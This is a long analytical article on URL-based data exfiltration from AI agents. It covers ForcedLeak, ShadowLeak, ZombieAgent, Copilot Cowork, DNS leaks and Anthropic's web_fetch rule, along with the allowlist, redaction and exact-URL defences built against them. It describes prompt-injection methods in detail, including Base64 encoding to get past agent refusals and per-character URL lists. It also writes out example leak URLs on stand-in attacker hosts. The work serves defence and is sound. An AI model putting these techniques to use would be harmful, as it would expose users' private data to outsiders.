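Salesforce sells customer relationship management (CRM) software, which companies use to keep records of their customers and sales. Its Agentforce platform lets AI agents work with those records. In July 2025 the security company Noma found that a stranger could make an agent leak these records by filling in a form on a company's public website. *ForcedLeak* (Nytro, 2025) reproduces Noma's full report.

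The form belonged to a Salesforce feature called Web-to-Lead, which saves each submission as a "lead", a record of a possible customer. Noma looked for a field with enough room for instructions. The fields for names, company and email address held only 40 or 80 characters, but the description field held 42,000.

The planted text did nothing until an employee asked Agentforce about the lead. In Noma's demonstration, the employee asked the agent to check the lead, answer the person's questions and draft a reply. The request was routine, but in making it the employee told the agent to act on whatever the description contained. The questions in the description led the agent to look up the email addresses of the company's other leads and put them in an image URL.

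Salesforce's Content Security Policy (CSP) should have stopped the browser from loading that image. Besides Salesforce's own page, it allowed images from 22 hosts, 15 of them with wildcards. One entry covered every subdomain of my-salesforce-cms.com, which had expired. Noma bought the domain for $5 and connected it to a rented server that logged every request. When the agent's reply appeared, the employee's browser requested the image, and that request carried the email addresses to Noma's server.

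Noma scored the flaw 9.4 out of 10. Noma does not say when the domain lapsed, so it is unclear how long it was available for an attacker to buy. The policy had other signs of neglect. It had a separate entry for all subdomains of vf.force.com, although the entry for force.com already covered them. It also allowed every subdomain of amazonaws.com and cloudinary.com, which are shared hosts, so an attacker might have exfiltrated data without buying a domain.

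Itay Ravia of Aim Labs told The Hacker News that ForcedLeak was a variant of EchoLeak, his group's attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot. Both attacks begin with an outsider planting text that the assistant later reads while answering an employee's question. In ForcedLeak, Noma owned the allowed host, so it didn't need the relay that EchoLeak required.

### What Salesforce changed

Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025, and Salesforce acknowledged it on 31 July. Willison, in *ForcedLeak*, writes that Salesforce first corrected its CSP and then added a check on the URLs its agents produce. This check, called Trusted URLs enforcement, began on 8 September. Salesforce also regained control of the expired domain, though Noma doesn't say when. Noma published its findings on 25 September.

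TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* reports that an administrator at each company must now approve any outside address that an agent generates or calls. In its notice to customers, Salesforce called the rule a "defense-in-depth control", meaning an extra layer of protection in case a prompt injection succeeds.

According to PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk*, Salesforce replaces every untrusted address in an Agentforce chat reply, including addresses inside HTML and CSS, with a fixed marker before the page displays the reply. The browser never receives the address, so it cannot load an image from it and the user cannot click on it. An image rule in a CSP would not prevent the click, because it does not restrict links.

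The check also gives customers more control over the list. In an older edition of Salesforce's documentation, *Manage Trusted URLs* says that Salesforce adds addresses of its own to the CSP, and that these do not appear among the customer's trusted URLs. The expired domain was presumably one of them. If so, an administrator reviewing the customer's list would not have seen it, although anyone could read it in the policy sent to the browser.

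Redaction alone might not have stopped ForcedLeak. TechNadu notes that standard Salesforce addresses remain trusted by default. If those defaults had included my-salesforce-cms.com, the new check would have approved it too. Recovering the domain closed the leak in either case.

Trusted URLs still checks an address by its domain, so an attacker could exfiltrate data through an approved host that offers accounts to the public, runs a relay, or lets outsiders see which of its addresses the model requests. Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* gives docs.google.com as an example of an address to add, but PromptArmor had extracted emails from Superhuman through a Google Form on that host. According to *Manage Trusted URLs*, a new entry allows images by default. PromptArmor advises administrators to turn images off for any host that doesn't need them. TechNadu points out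 that each entry applies to the company's whole Salesforce system, not just its agents.

Redaction also doesn't protect data that an agent sends through its tools. For that data, PromptArmor recommends other defences, such as asking a person to confirm each action. Salesforce's *Security Advisories* records that in August 2025 the company began requiring confirmation for several agent actions, including password resets and order cancellations. These confirmations would not have stopped ForcedLeak, because it needed only an image.

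A year later, researchers at Zenity Labs got past the redaction itself. Their attack, SalesBleed, also began with a Web-to-Lead form. Antipov (2026) explains in the Russian news report *Один вредоносный лид против всей CRM* that the check mishandled some domain endings and special character sequences, so an untrusted address could remain in the agent's reply. The agent sometimes told the employee that security policy had blocked the content even though the data had already left.

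Zenity reported SalesBleed on 1 June 2026. Poireault (2026) writes in *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk* that Salesforce fixed the redaction on 18 August. Antipov writes that by 21 September Zenity had confirmed fixes for the whole attack, including a related problem in Slack. SalesBleed did not depend on an expired domain, so better upkeep of the allowlist would not have prevented it.

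### How often trust outlives ownership

In *Zombies in Alternate Realities*, Thottungal Valapu, Jonker and Sommese (2026) measured how often other systems keep trusting a domain after its original owner no longer controls it. They studied web certificates, the Ethereum Name Service (ENS), which connects domains to cryptocurrency wallets, and Maven Central, a library of Java software whose publishers identify themselves by domain.

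Registries do not publish full ownership histories, so the researchers reconstructed them from registration records, daily lists of active domains and their own daily scans. They treated a new registration date, or a gap of at least 80 days in a domain's activity, as the end of one owner's control. They called a link a "zombie" if it was still valid after that.

| System | When it checks who controls the domain | Share of links that were zombies |
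|---|---|---|
| Certificates for newly registered domains | When issuing the certificate, which then expires | About 2.7% |
| Maven Central | Once | 15.2% (4,842 of 31,853) |
| ENS links stored on the blockchain | Once | About 24% |
| ENS links checked through the domain name system | On every use | None, by design |

An allowlist entry is most like the links in the two middle rows, except that a developer may never have checked who owned the domain. The percentages suggest that stale entries will build up on a list that nobody rechecks. They are not estimates for allowlists, since a company probably renews a domain it uses for pictures more reliably than a hobbyist renews one attached to a cryptocurrency wallet. The ENS links had been accumulating for about seven years, and no new owner had replaced any of the zombies.

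The true shares are probably higher. The researchers could not detect sales in which the registration continued under a new owner, and their 80-day threshold misses some domains that a buyer registered as soon as they became available.

A domain can also change hands through theft. *Domijn* (2026) tested the security of registrars and their resellers, and its main finding was that they implemented two-factor authentication improperly. An attacker who gets into the owner's registrar account may be able to take the domain before the registration expires.

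Criminals have exploited this kind of leftover trust on websites. *What Gets Measured Gets Managed* (2025) describes how attackers registered the old domain of an analytics service that had closed in 2014. A 2022 report found that they had used it to steal card details through more than 40 online shops that were still loading the service's code. Thottungal Valapu and colleagues also found 214 Maven Central publishers that released new software after someone re-registered their domains, though they have not established whether any of it was malicious.

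### Abandoned subdomains

An attacker can sometimes take over part of a domain that its owner still pays for. Suppose Marta's office rents a cloud server for pictures and adds a domain name system (DNS) record that directs `pictures.office.example` to the server's network address. Later, the office cancels the server but forgets to delete the record. The cloud company gives the address to another customer, who then receives every request for `pictures.office.example`. An attacker can keep renting servers until they get that address.

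*Can I Take Your Subdomain?* (2020) calls these leftover records "dangling" and describes several ways they arise. For example, a record may point to another domain that has expired, or to a closed account at a hosting service. Some owners also use a DNS wildcard, a single record that directs every possible subdomain to one service. If the service lets customers claim names freely, an attacker can choose a new subdomain and attach it to their own account.

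Estimates of how common dangling records are depend on where researchers looked. *Cloudy with a Chance of Cyberattacks* (2024) cites one earlier study that found over 700,000 domains pointing to cloud addresses that were available to rent, and another that found about 10,000 subdomains with dangling records among the million most popular domains. The paper also documents attackers using such subdomains.

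A wildcard on an allowlist makes this worse. If the chat site allows `*.office.example`, the attacker can use any subdomain the office has abandoned, including ones that never hosted pictures. Listing a full host name instead limits the risk to that host.

### Keeping a list current

The simplest precaution is to remove entries that nobody needs, which requires a record of why each host is on the list and who asked for it. To remove my-salesforce-cms.com, Salesforce would have had to notice that the domain had lapsed, but a developer reading the policy could easily have mistaken it for a working Salesforce domain.

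A company that retires a domain should remove it from every allowlist before letting the registration lapse. Renewing the domain for a few more years costs little and protects people who still use old versions of the software. Automatic renewal and strong two-factor authentication at the registrar reduce the chance of losing domains still in use.

Software can also check ownership through RDAP, a public lookup service for domain registrations that gives the date the current registration began. If that date is later than the date on the allowlist entry, someone has registered the domain again since the developer approved it, and the software should disable the entry. This would have caught my-salesforce-cms.com after Noma bought it, and before the purchase the same lookup would have found no registration. The date check would miss a sale, a theft or an abandoned subdomain, and some registries,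 including Germany's .de, don't supply the date.

*What Gets Measured Gets Managed* proposes a similar rule that blocks requests to newly registered domains, including those on CSP allowlists. An attacker could evade this rule by waiting until the domain no longer counted as new, unless the software also recorded that it had expired. A more cautious system, *DomainHarvester* (2024), builds allowlists of trustworthy but rarely visited sites. It rejects domains that have used an expired certificate, even if the owner later replaced it, and domains that have recently shown a registrar's placeholder page. A company could use these signals to decide which allowlist entries a person should review.

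Thottungal Valapu and colleagues think the most effective defence is to check a domain's ownership every time it is used. A browser applying a CSP does not check who owns a domain, so the website's server would have to do so before sending the policy. A daily check would take less work, and any change it can detect would go unnoticed for at most about a day.

Their second choice is an expiry date, which limits the damage when other checks fail. If each allowlist entry lasts 90 days and a domain is equally likely to change hands on any day, a stale entry stays active for 45 days on average. Issuers revoked only 4.3% of the zombie certificates early, and the rest stayed valid until they expired, which suggests that deadlines work better than relying on people to notice a problem. An expiry date helps only if someone confirms the domain's owner before extending the entry. *Manage Trusted URLs*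 describes a way to switch an entry off by hand, but no expiry date.

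## Requests that never reach the allowlist check

A sound allowlist has to cover every request, whichever program sends it and by whatever method. Security engineers call this requirement complete mediation.

Suppose Marta's office sets its chat site's image rule to `'none'`, the strictest possible setting, so the browser loads no pictures there. But the assistant can also post reminders in the office's messaging program, which does show pictures. The hidden text in the newsletter now leads the model to put the attacker's picture in a reminder. The chat site's rule doesn't apply in the messaging program, so when Marta opens the reminder, the program requests the picture and the attacker reads 7315 in the log.

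A useful test for a real leak is whether it would have worked with an empty allowlist. If so, choosing hosts more carefully could not have prevented it. The developer has to find the unchecked path and either close it or add a check to it.

### Messages that other programs display

Messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram fetch linked pages to show previews, so an assistant that replies in one of them can leak data through a plain link even if nobody clicks it.

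In 2024, Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* showed how this works in Slack, which by default previewed every link that users or Slack apps posted. Rehberger had a program post a link to his website, then found a request from Slackbot, Slack's link-fetching software, in his server's log. Developers can prevent these requests by turning off two preview options in the messages their apps send.

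PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* found the same problem in 2026 with OpenClaw, an AI agent that people can instruct through messaging apps. OpenClaw was exposed by default on Telegram. PromptArmor built a website that records what each preview request contains, so people could test other combinations of agent and app. One log PromptArmor published included a name and an API key. The researchers stopped the leak by turning off link previews in OpenClaw's Telegram settings, but each user has to do this themselves, and PromptArmor does not report that the default has changed.

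A network gateway would not have helped much, because the agent contacts only Telegram and the attacker's address is just part of the message. Telegram acts as a relay here, like Bing's image search. The gateway could stop the leak by blocking Telegram, but then the user couldn't talk to the agent.

Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent for office work, leaked files through messages to its own user. According to Microsoft's documentation, Cowork asked permission before sending an email or posting in Teams. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* found that Cowork did not ask when the recipient was the user, and that users could not change this. Willison covered the attack on 26 May 2026 in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*.

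In the demonstration, the victim uploads a "skill", a file of instructions for a particular task, that someone else has published online. Five of its 81 lines are hostile. When the victim asks for a review of the week's work, Cowork posts a Teams message containing images hosted on the attacker's site. The image addresses include download links for the victim's files. When the victim opens the message, Teams requests the images, which sends the links to the attacker. Anyone with such a link can download the file without logging in, so a short address is enough to leak a whole document.

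The attack worked in all five trials. It also worked on Claude Opus 4.7, which leaked more documents than the model Cowork chose automatically because it searched for them more thoroughly.

Microsoft's approval rule considered only who would receive a message, although displaying the message also sent requests to any hosts in its image URLs. The exception for messages to oneself seems reasonable as far as recipients are concerned, since such a message tells nobody else anything. PromptArmor published the attack as a risk in the product's design and reports no fix. Administrators can block downloads from SharePoint, but employees then can't print or sync the affected files, or open them in desktop programs such as Word.

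PromptArmor later found another way to get data out of Cowork, and Microsoft fixed this one. Cowork runs code in a sandbox that is supposed to have no network access. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Controlled by Attacker, Bypassing Sandbox* describes a service outside the sandbox that copied files in and out and would fetch a file from any URL it received. A script in a hostile skill could send out private data by putting it in a URL on the attacker's server and giving that URL to the service.

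The service also saved the server's reply in the sandbox, where the script read it and ran any commands it contained. This let an attacker explore the victim's email and files one command at a time, even after the victim pressed the stop button, because background programs kept running. PromptArmor reported the flaw on 24 June 2026, and Microsoft confirmed on 19 August that it had been mitigated. An allowlist on the sandbox's own connection would not have stopped the attack. The file service needed its own rule, such as accepting only addresses in the company's storage.

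### Checks that cover only some requests

A check can also miss requests within a single product. ChatGPT's url_safe check missed requests in the iPhone app, and in SearchLeak, Copilot's code block came too late to catch them.

The consumer version of Copilot had a safeguard that removed private data from a web address before Copilot opened it. The safeguard was not a domain allowlist, but it also failed because some requests were never checked. According to *Reprompt* (Taler, 2026), it applied only to the first request. Researchers at Varonis told Copilot to do everything twice and compare the results. In a test with an invented secret phrase, the safeguard removed the phrase from the first address, but the second still contained it. Taler suspects that Microsoft limited the check to keep Copilot fast.

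As in SearchLeak, the attack began when the victim clicked a link containing the attacker's prompt. The attacker's server could then answer each request with another question, such as where the victim lived or what they had last discussed with Copilot. The exchange continued even if the victim closed the tab. The flaw did not affect Microsoft 365 Copilot, and Microsoft had patched it by 30 March 2026.

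A check on web requests can also miss DNS lookups, which convert a host name into a network address. ChatGPT runs Python programs in an isolated environment that blocked direct connections to outside servers, but Check Point Research found in *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) that it still allowed DNS lookups. The owner of a domain can run the server that answers lookups for its subdomains, so a program that looks up `7315.attacker.example` sends Marta's alarm code, 7315, to the attacker without opening a web page.

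The researchers could also send commands back in the answers to the lookups. In one demonstration, they built a custom version of ChatGPT that acted as a personal doctor. The user uploaded laboratory results and described symptoms, and the attacker's server received the patient's name and ChatGPT's medical assessment. When the user asked whether the data had gone anywhere, ChatGPT said it had not.

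OpenAI had already found the underlying problem itself, and it finished deploying a fix on 20 February 2026. Check Point concluded that protecting these systems requires control over "every possible outbound communication path", which is close to a definition of complete mediation. For a sandbox with a domain allowlist, this means blocking lookups of unlisted domains as well as web requests to them.

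### CoSnitch's direct route

CoSnitch, another Varonis attack on the consumer version of Copilot, got attention mainly for how the researchers found it. They kept asking Copilot why a link could not run a prompt automatically, and its explanation of the protections revealed an undocumented URL setting that made this possible.

Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes a prompt that told Copilot to search the victim's connected accounts, such as Gmail or Google Drive, and write what it found into a web address. The prompt then asked Copilot to summarise the page at that address. Copilot's built-in tool for reading web pages sent the request straight to a server whose log the researchers could read. The attack did not need an image, a relay or an account on an allowed host.

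Varonis does not describe any check on where this tool could send requests, so CoSnitch is not evidence that an allowlist failed or that an attacker bypassed one. Varonis also doesn't say whether the safeguard from Reprompt was active. It notes that encoding the data helps to avoid filters that look for passwords and keys. Some of the test requests went to webhook.site, and even a fairly crude allowlist on the tool would have blocked those unless it included that site, as Antigravity's did.

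Varonis reported CoSnitch in December 2025, and Microsoft released patches on 18 August 2026. TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot* lists the flaw as CVE-2026-24301, with a severity of 8.8 out of 10, and says that how Microsoft fixed it is unknown.

### A setting that left a tool behind

Administrators can turn off web search for a whole organisation in Rovo, Atlassian's AI assistant. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* found that this disabled searching but left the tool that opens search results available. That tool would open any URL, including one the model had just written.

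In PromptArmor's demonstration, the victim uploads a guide containing hidden instructions and asks Rovo to organise some Jira tickets. Rovo then sends the contents of tickets and Confluence documents to the attacker's website without asking for approval. If the victim reopens the chat later, it shows only the suggested changes to the tickets. Rovo also displayed Markdown images, which gave attackers a second way to extract data.

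Turning off web search did not stop Rovo from contacting the web, because another feature could send the same requests. Restricting the list of search sites would not have affected that feature either. An administrator who turns off web search may reasonably assume that the setting blocks all web access.

PromptArmor reported the flaw on 23 May 2026. Atlassian thanked the researchers but then stopped responding, and Rovo was still vulnerable when they published more than two months later. Atlassian did fix a separate flaw, which Varonis described in *RovoBlast* (2026), published on 7 August. That attack required a user to click a link and, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover RovoBlast Vulnerability in Atlassian AI Assistant*, sent data out through Rovo's browsing agent. It is unclear whether the fix also closed the route PromptArmor reported.

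### What Lockdown Mode restricts

OpenAI's Lockdown Mode limits or turns off many ChatGPT features that can send requests, instead of relying on an allowlist of safe hosts.

According to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026), Lockdown Mode launched on 13 February for organisations with ChatGPT's Enterprise, Edu, Healthcare and Teachers plans, and OpenAI began extending it to personal accounts and to businesses that manage their own subscriptions on 4 June. Sources therefore date the launch differently. The Hacker News dates it to June 2026, when most individual users could first turn the mode on, while Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, writes that OpenAI "first teased" it in February.

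OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, the help page for the setting, lists what changes:

| Feature | With Lockdown Mode on |
|---|---|
| Web browsing | Cached pages only |
| Images | ChatGPT may not show them in ordinary replies or retrieve them from the web |
| Deep research and agent mode | Off |
| Code written in Canvas, ChatGPT's editing space | Users cannot approve network access |
| File downloads for data analysis | Off, though users can still upload files |
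| Connected apps | Restricted on personal accounts, but left to administrators in managed workspaces |
| Memory, file uploads and sharing of conversations | No change |
| Network access in Codex | No change |

Limiting browsing to cached pages is a stronger defense than a domain allowlist. If ChatGPT reads only copies stored on OpenAI's network, the attacker cannot see which pages it opens, so the model cannot leak a secret through its choice of pages. This holds as long as a request for an uncached page doesn't trigger a live fetch.

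Connected apps are harder to restrict because many people need them for work. OpenAI advises administrators not to let an app write or change anything unless they are confident that an attacker could not see the result. A sound allowlist has to meet the same condition for web requests.

Willison welcomed Lockdown Mode because its limits do not depend on an AI model's judgement, which an attacker could manipulate. He pointed out that its existence implies ChatGPT's default settings do not reliably protect against a determined attacker. OpenAI does not guarantee that the mode will stop every leak, and warns of risks from connected apps, unforeseen combinations of features and new techniques.

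### The pop-up that escaped

Check Point found an unforeseen combination of this kind. In February 2026 ChatGPT gained a feature that displays a working preview of a web page when a reply contains the page's code. Because a stranger may have written the code, OpenAI put the preview inside two nested frames, which are sections of a page that can have their own restrictions. If the previewed page tried to contact an outside server, ChatGPT showed the user an approval prompt.

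Duggan (2026), in *Check Point Bypassed ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode With a Popup*, explains how pop-up windows got around Lockdown Mode's limits. The browser's rules for the frames allowed pop-ups to open without the frames' restrictions. OpenAI relied on a second layer of protection, replacing the page's normal command for opening a window with a version that asked for approval. But a page can create another frame inside itself, with its own copy of the original command. A pop-up opened with that copy did not trigger the approval request, and Lockdown Mode's limits did not apply to it.

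An attacker could deliver the code through a prompt, a shared chat or a custom version of ChatGPT. In the ChatGPT Classic desktop app, the pop-up opened without a click. A hostile custom version could therefore send the whole chat history to the attacker's server while the user talked to it. The attacker could also disguise the pop-up as a ChatGPT update to spread malware.

Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* describes an HTML preview in Microsoft 365 Copilot as another exfiltration channel, one of a group of flaws that Microsoft has since patched. The ReLeak attacks through Copilot's new documents and its Python sandbox also used features that a browser's image rule does not cover.

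OpenAI told Check Point on 18 September 2026 that it had fixed the Lockdown Mode bypass, and Check Point confirmed that the method no longer worked. TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* reports that OpenAI made the change on its own servers. Check Point published its findings on 5 November and reported no real attacks.

The repair removed both pop-up permissions from the outer frame. OpenAI's earlier protection had replaced a command in one page, so it missed the copy in a frame that the page created later. The browser itself enforces the new restriction. A frame cannot regain a permission that its parent frame lacks, so the restriction also covers frames that OpenAI's developers did not anticipate.

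## Approving exact URLs instead of domains

Many of the leaks described so far passed a check because the host was on an allowlist, even though the rest of the URL contained private data. An exact-URL check examines the complete URL and approves it only if a source with no access to the private data had already recorded it.

In its January 2026 post, OpenAI says its software now checks whether the exact address has already appeared on the public web independently of any user's data, instead of deciding whether the site is trustworthy. Suppose Marta's alarm code, 7315, is in her mailbox. If an address ending in `ref=7315` isn't on any public page, the model may have just created it using her code, but if the address is on a public page, whoever published it did so without seeing her mail.

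| Address | Domain allowlist | Exact-URL check |
|---|---|---|
| `https://newsletter-art.storage.example/banner.png?ref=7315` | Loads if the storage company is listed | Stops the request |
| `https://search.example/go?to=https://pictures.attacker.example/7315.png` | Loads if the search engine is listed | Stops the request |
| An article on a small newspaper's site | Blocked unless someone listed the site | Loads if the article is already known |
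| `https://pictures.attacker.example/7.png` | Blocked | Loads if the picture is already known |

The first two rows show why nobody has to review whether attackers can open accounts with storage companies or relay requests through search engines. In the last row, the check accepts an image on the attacker's own server because the image's URL contains no private data.

### ShadowLeak

The security company Radware had demonstrated two attacks on ChatGPT before OpenAI publicly described this rule. Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes the first, which targeted Deep Research, a ChatGPT mode that reads web pages and then writes a report. Users could also connect Deep Research to Gmail. In the demonstration, an outsider sent an email with hidden instructions to find an employee's name and home address in the inbox and open a supposed staff directory with those details in the URL. When the user asked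 for research on the day's emails, the agent followed the hidden instructions without asking for confirmation.

The researchers' first attempts failed. The agent refused plain requests to send personal data, and it treated the attacker's address as suspicious, searching for it on the web instead of opening it. The researchers then asked the agent about its tools and learned the name of the one that opens pages. When they told the agent to use that tool and to retry after failures, some requests went through, but often without the personal data. Finally, they told the agent to encode the data in Base64, a standard way of rewriting data as letters, digits and a few symbols, on the pretext of protecting it. The attack then succeeded in every repeated test. According to Radware, this worked because the software carrying out the request received only a harmless-looking string.

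The request came from OpenAI's servers, where neither a browser policy nor an employer's network filter could detect it. Radware found no restriction like url_safe on the addresses the agent could open, so this attack had no allowlist to bypass. Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025. OpenAI fixed it in early August without telling the researchers and marked it as resolved on 3 September.

### ZombieAgent

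According to Radware's *ZombieAgent*, OpenAI then restricted ChatGPT to opening URLs exactly as it received them, so it would not add parameters even when told to. This blocked ShadowLeak's method, but ChatGPT still accepted URLs from the attacker's email.

Radware's Zvika Babo therefore put a ready-made list of URLs in the email, one for each letter and digit and one for a space. ChatGPT spelled out private data by opening the matching URLs in turn. To preserve the order, Babo gave each character a different URL for each position, so a block of ten characters needed 260 URLs for letters and 100 for digits. The attack began when the user asked ChatGPT to do anything with Gmail.

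OpenAI had also tried to keep attackers from making such a leak permanent. ChatGPT could not use its memory after using a connector such as Gmail in the same chat, and it would not open an attacker's URLs stored in memory. Babo found that ChatGPT could still read its memory first and then use a connector. A hostile file could therefore make ChatGPT save an instruction in memory to read an email from the attacker whenever the user sent a message. That email contained the URLs for leaking data. In another version, ChatGPT leaked email addresses from the inbox, and the attacker's server sent the same hostile email to each one.

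Radware reported ZombieAgent on 26 September 2025. Bugcrowd, which handles such reports for OpenAI, reproduced it four days later, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December.

The news report *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack as a vicious cycle in AI* says that after the fix, ChatGPT no longer opened every link from an email but would open one that appeared in a well-known public index. The report blames the flaw on OpenAI's failure to stop ChatGPT from adding a single letter to a URL. Radware writes that ChatGPT never added anything. Radware's account fits the fix better, because a ban on adding letters would not have stopped an attack that used a list of URLs already containing them.

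### OpenAI's index of public addresses

A crawler builds the index by following links around the web and recording the addresses it finds, as a search engine does. OpenAI's crawler has no access to conversations, accounts or personal data. When ChatGPT is about to load a page or image automatically, the software looks for the exact address in the index and allows the request if the address is there. Otherwise, the software either tells the agent to try a different website or warns the user that the link is unverified and may include information from the conversation. The warning shows the address and lets the user copy or open it.

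In discussing OpenAI's accompanying paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, Embrace The Red notes that ChatGPT also seems to accept any address the user has entered in the chat. This is reasonable for addresses the user typed, but users may also paste text they have not checked, which Samoilenko's 2023 attack relied on.

Rehberger dates these measures to around August 2025. ZombieAgent still worked in late September with URLs copied from an email, so the index check probably did not apply to such URLs at first.

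Comparing complete addresses also removes most of the danger from redirects, which was one of OpenAI's reasons for rejecting a list of trusted sites. A search engine's redirect to `7315.png` is not in the index, so the first request is never sent. An indexed address may also redirect, but its server has usually received nothing secret to pass on. A site that recognises a logged-in user, however, could redirect to an address containing that person's details. Looking up the new address after every redirect would prevent this.

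OpenAI guarantees only that the safeguards prevent an agent from quietly leaking user-specific data "through the URL itself". As worded, this does not cover an address the user opens after a warning, or what an attacker can learn from which of two approved addresses the agent opens. OpenAI also says the check does not make a page's content trustworthy, remove hostile instructions from it or stop a site from deceiving the user. It treats the check as one layer of protection, alongside training against prompt injection, monitoring and its own test attacks.

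The check can protect only the features that use it, and Rehberger warns that some developers at OpenAI may not know it exists. That might explain the leak from ChatGPT that Yang and colleagues recorded six days after OpenAI's post.

### Anthropic's rule for web_fetch

Anthropic introduced a similar rule in September 2025 with web_fetch, a tool that lets Claude read web pages. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* explains that Claude may not construct an address. It can fetch only one that has already appeared in the conversation, in any of these places:

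- a message from the user
- the output of a tool that the developer's own software runs
- the results of an earlier web search or fetch

The tool also rejects URLs longer than 250 characters. Anthropic warned that some risk remained and advised developers concerned about leaks to limit the number of fetches, list the permitted domains or turn the tool off.

OpenAI builds its index outside the conversation, whereas Anthropic accepted addresses from much of the conversation itself, as url_safe had in 2023. This is a weakness, as Willison noticed the day he covered the tool, because many applications insert untrusted text into what the API treats as the user's message. If an application put the day's email there, and one email contained a list of addresses like ZombieAgent's, the tool would approve them all. Willison still thought the ban on constructed addresses protected well against the usual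 attack, in which the model adds private data to a URL.

### How links in fetched pages broke the rule

In July 2026 Ayush Paul got data out through the links in pages Claude had fetched (*The Memory Heist*, dated 9 July by dyb in *The Read-Only Lie*). Paul built a website for a fake coffee shop. According to Willison (2026), it showed hostile text only to software that identified itself as Claude's, so a person checking the site would have seen nothing wrong. The text claimed that an AI assistant had to identify itself by finding its user's profile in an alphabetical directory, one letter at a time.

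Suppose Marta's assistant follows Anthropic's original rule and fetches a page with ten links, `/0` to `/9`. Hidden text on the page tells the model to find the entry for the alarm code. The model opens `/7`, and the attacker's server returns a page with ten longer links, `/70` to `/79`. The model opens `/73`, then `/731`, then `/7315`. The last address contains the whole code, yet the model copied every address from a page it had fetched.

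The check failed because those pages depended on the secret. The server offered `/7315` only after the model had opened `/731`. Writing the links during the attack also took less preparation than Babo's method, which needed a separate address for every character and position. Paul's server could extend the text for as long as Claude kept following links.

Each of Paul's pages had 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen. Claude used them to spell out the user's name, home city and employer, which it knew or had inferred from its memory of earlier chats. According to dyb, the user had never stated the city, and Claude inferred it from the name of a high school hackathon. dyb estimates that the leak took about 30 fetches, all in one turn of the conversation.

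Anthropic did not pay Paul a bounty, saying it had already found the flaw itself. By 15 July it had stopped web_fetch in the Claude app from following links inside fetched pages.

### What developers still have to change

Anthropic's developer platform still allows the same route by default. *Web fetch 工具*, a newer edition of the documentation in Chinese, still lists fetched pages as a permitted source of URLs. Developers can exclude them with the `url_sources` setting.

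Anthropic added a version of the rule to Managed Agents, its service for running agents, on 7 October 2026, three months after Paul's demonstration. Anthropic's *Claude Platform release notes* (2026) say the change reduces the risk of exfiltration, but this version also accepts links from pages the agent has fetched.

| Where the address appeared | Anthropic's API, default setting | Managed Agents |
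|---|---|---|
| User's message | Accepted | Accepted |
| Search result | Accepted | Accepted |
| Page fetched earlier | Accepted | Accepted |
| Output of a command-line tool | Accepted if the developer's software runs the tool | Refused |
| Claude's own text | Refused | Refused |

The API's treatment of command-line tools creates a second weakness. Claude could write a program that prints an address containing a secret. If the developer's software runs that program, the printed address counts as a tool result, so Claude can fetch it. Wu and colleagues got new addresses past url_safe similarly, by passing them through an online document. Anthropic's documentation warns about the risk from command-line tools and shows how to exclude them by name.

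The API also refuses an address that seems to contain a password or API key, unless the developer or user supplied it. This check would not have stopped Paul, because a person's name does not look like a password.

A developer can combine the rule with a domain allowlist. Since 20 October, administrators have been able to set an organisation-wide allowlist for web_fetch. In Managed Agents, every address, including any reached through a redirect, must be allowed by both the organisation's list and the agent's own. An allowlist would have kept Claude away from Paul's site, but also from most of the web.

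### The leak through indexed pages

Anthropic's rule is close to OpenAI's once fetched pages are excluded. Both accept URLs from the user and from a search of the public web, so an attacker can still make the model spell out a secret by requesting indexed pages. Rehberger notes that OpenAI acknowledges this in its paper.

This is much slower than putting the data in a single address. Superhuman's assistant sent the full text of several emails through one Google Forms link. Spelling out one email of 1,000 letters and digits would take 1,000 requests with 36 indexed pages, or 431 with 4,096 pages. That many requests to one site would be fairly easy to detect.

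But leaking a short secret takes only a few requests, and the secret can give the attacker access to a long document, as the download links leaked from Copilot Cowork did.

Rehberger's proposals to cache responses or forbid repeat visits would not have stopped ZombieAgent, because its list already had a different URL for every character position. But they would require an attacker to get 360 pages into the index, instead of 36, to send ten characters that could arrive in any order. The limits seem worth adopting because they would add a modest obstacle and seldom inconvenience users.

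dyb suggests looking for a pattern like the one in Paul's attack, a quick series of requests to one site in which each path is one character longer than the last. This would catch a copy of Paul's site. An attacker could avoid it by giving the links random names and labelling them with letters on the page.

A more complete fix, similar to Lockdown Mode's restriction to cached pages, would be to give the model a copy of the page that the crawler saved before the conversation began. Rehberger's cache still needs one live request for each page, and the attacker sees that request. The main drawback of saved copies is that they may be out of date, which matters for train times and share prices.

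### Blocked pages and ignored warnings

An exact-URL check also stops many harmless requests. A public index may not include a parcel-tracking link, a document shared with a few colleagues or an article published ten minutes ago. OpenAI's post gives no figure for how often ChatGPT encounters such URLs.

OpenAI rejected a list of trusted sites partly because it expected the list to trigger too many warnings. People read many sites beyond the most popular ones, and frequent false alarms can train them to click through without thinking. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026) also describes domain lists as impractical for assistants that need varied sources. A broad web index should cause fewer false alarms than a short list of domains, but users still have to judge any address missing from the index.

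Seeing the address may not help a user much if the data in it is encoded. If a warning showed Marta a link ending in `ref=7315`, she might recognise the alarm code. In Base64 the same link could end in `ref=NzMxNQ`, which looks like the tracking codes in many ordinary links. According to *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data*, even detailed logs often cut addresses short, and software that looks for encoded data raises many false alarms because ordinary applications encode their parameters too.

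OpenAI advises users not to open the link if they are unsure, and to ask for another source instead. Its software can also send the agent to a different website without involving the user, which avoids the risk of a careless click. Switching sources works well when several pages answer the same question, but not when the user needs a particular page that is not in the index.

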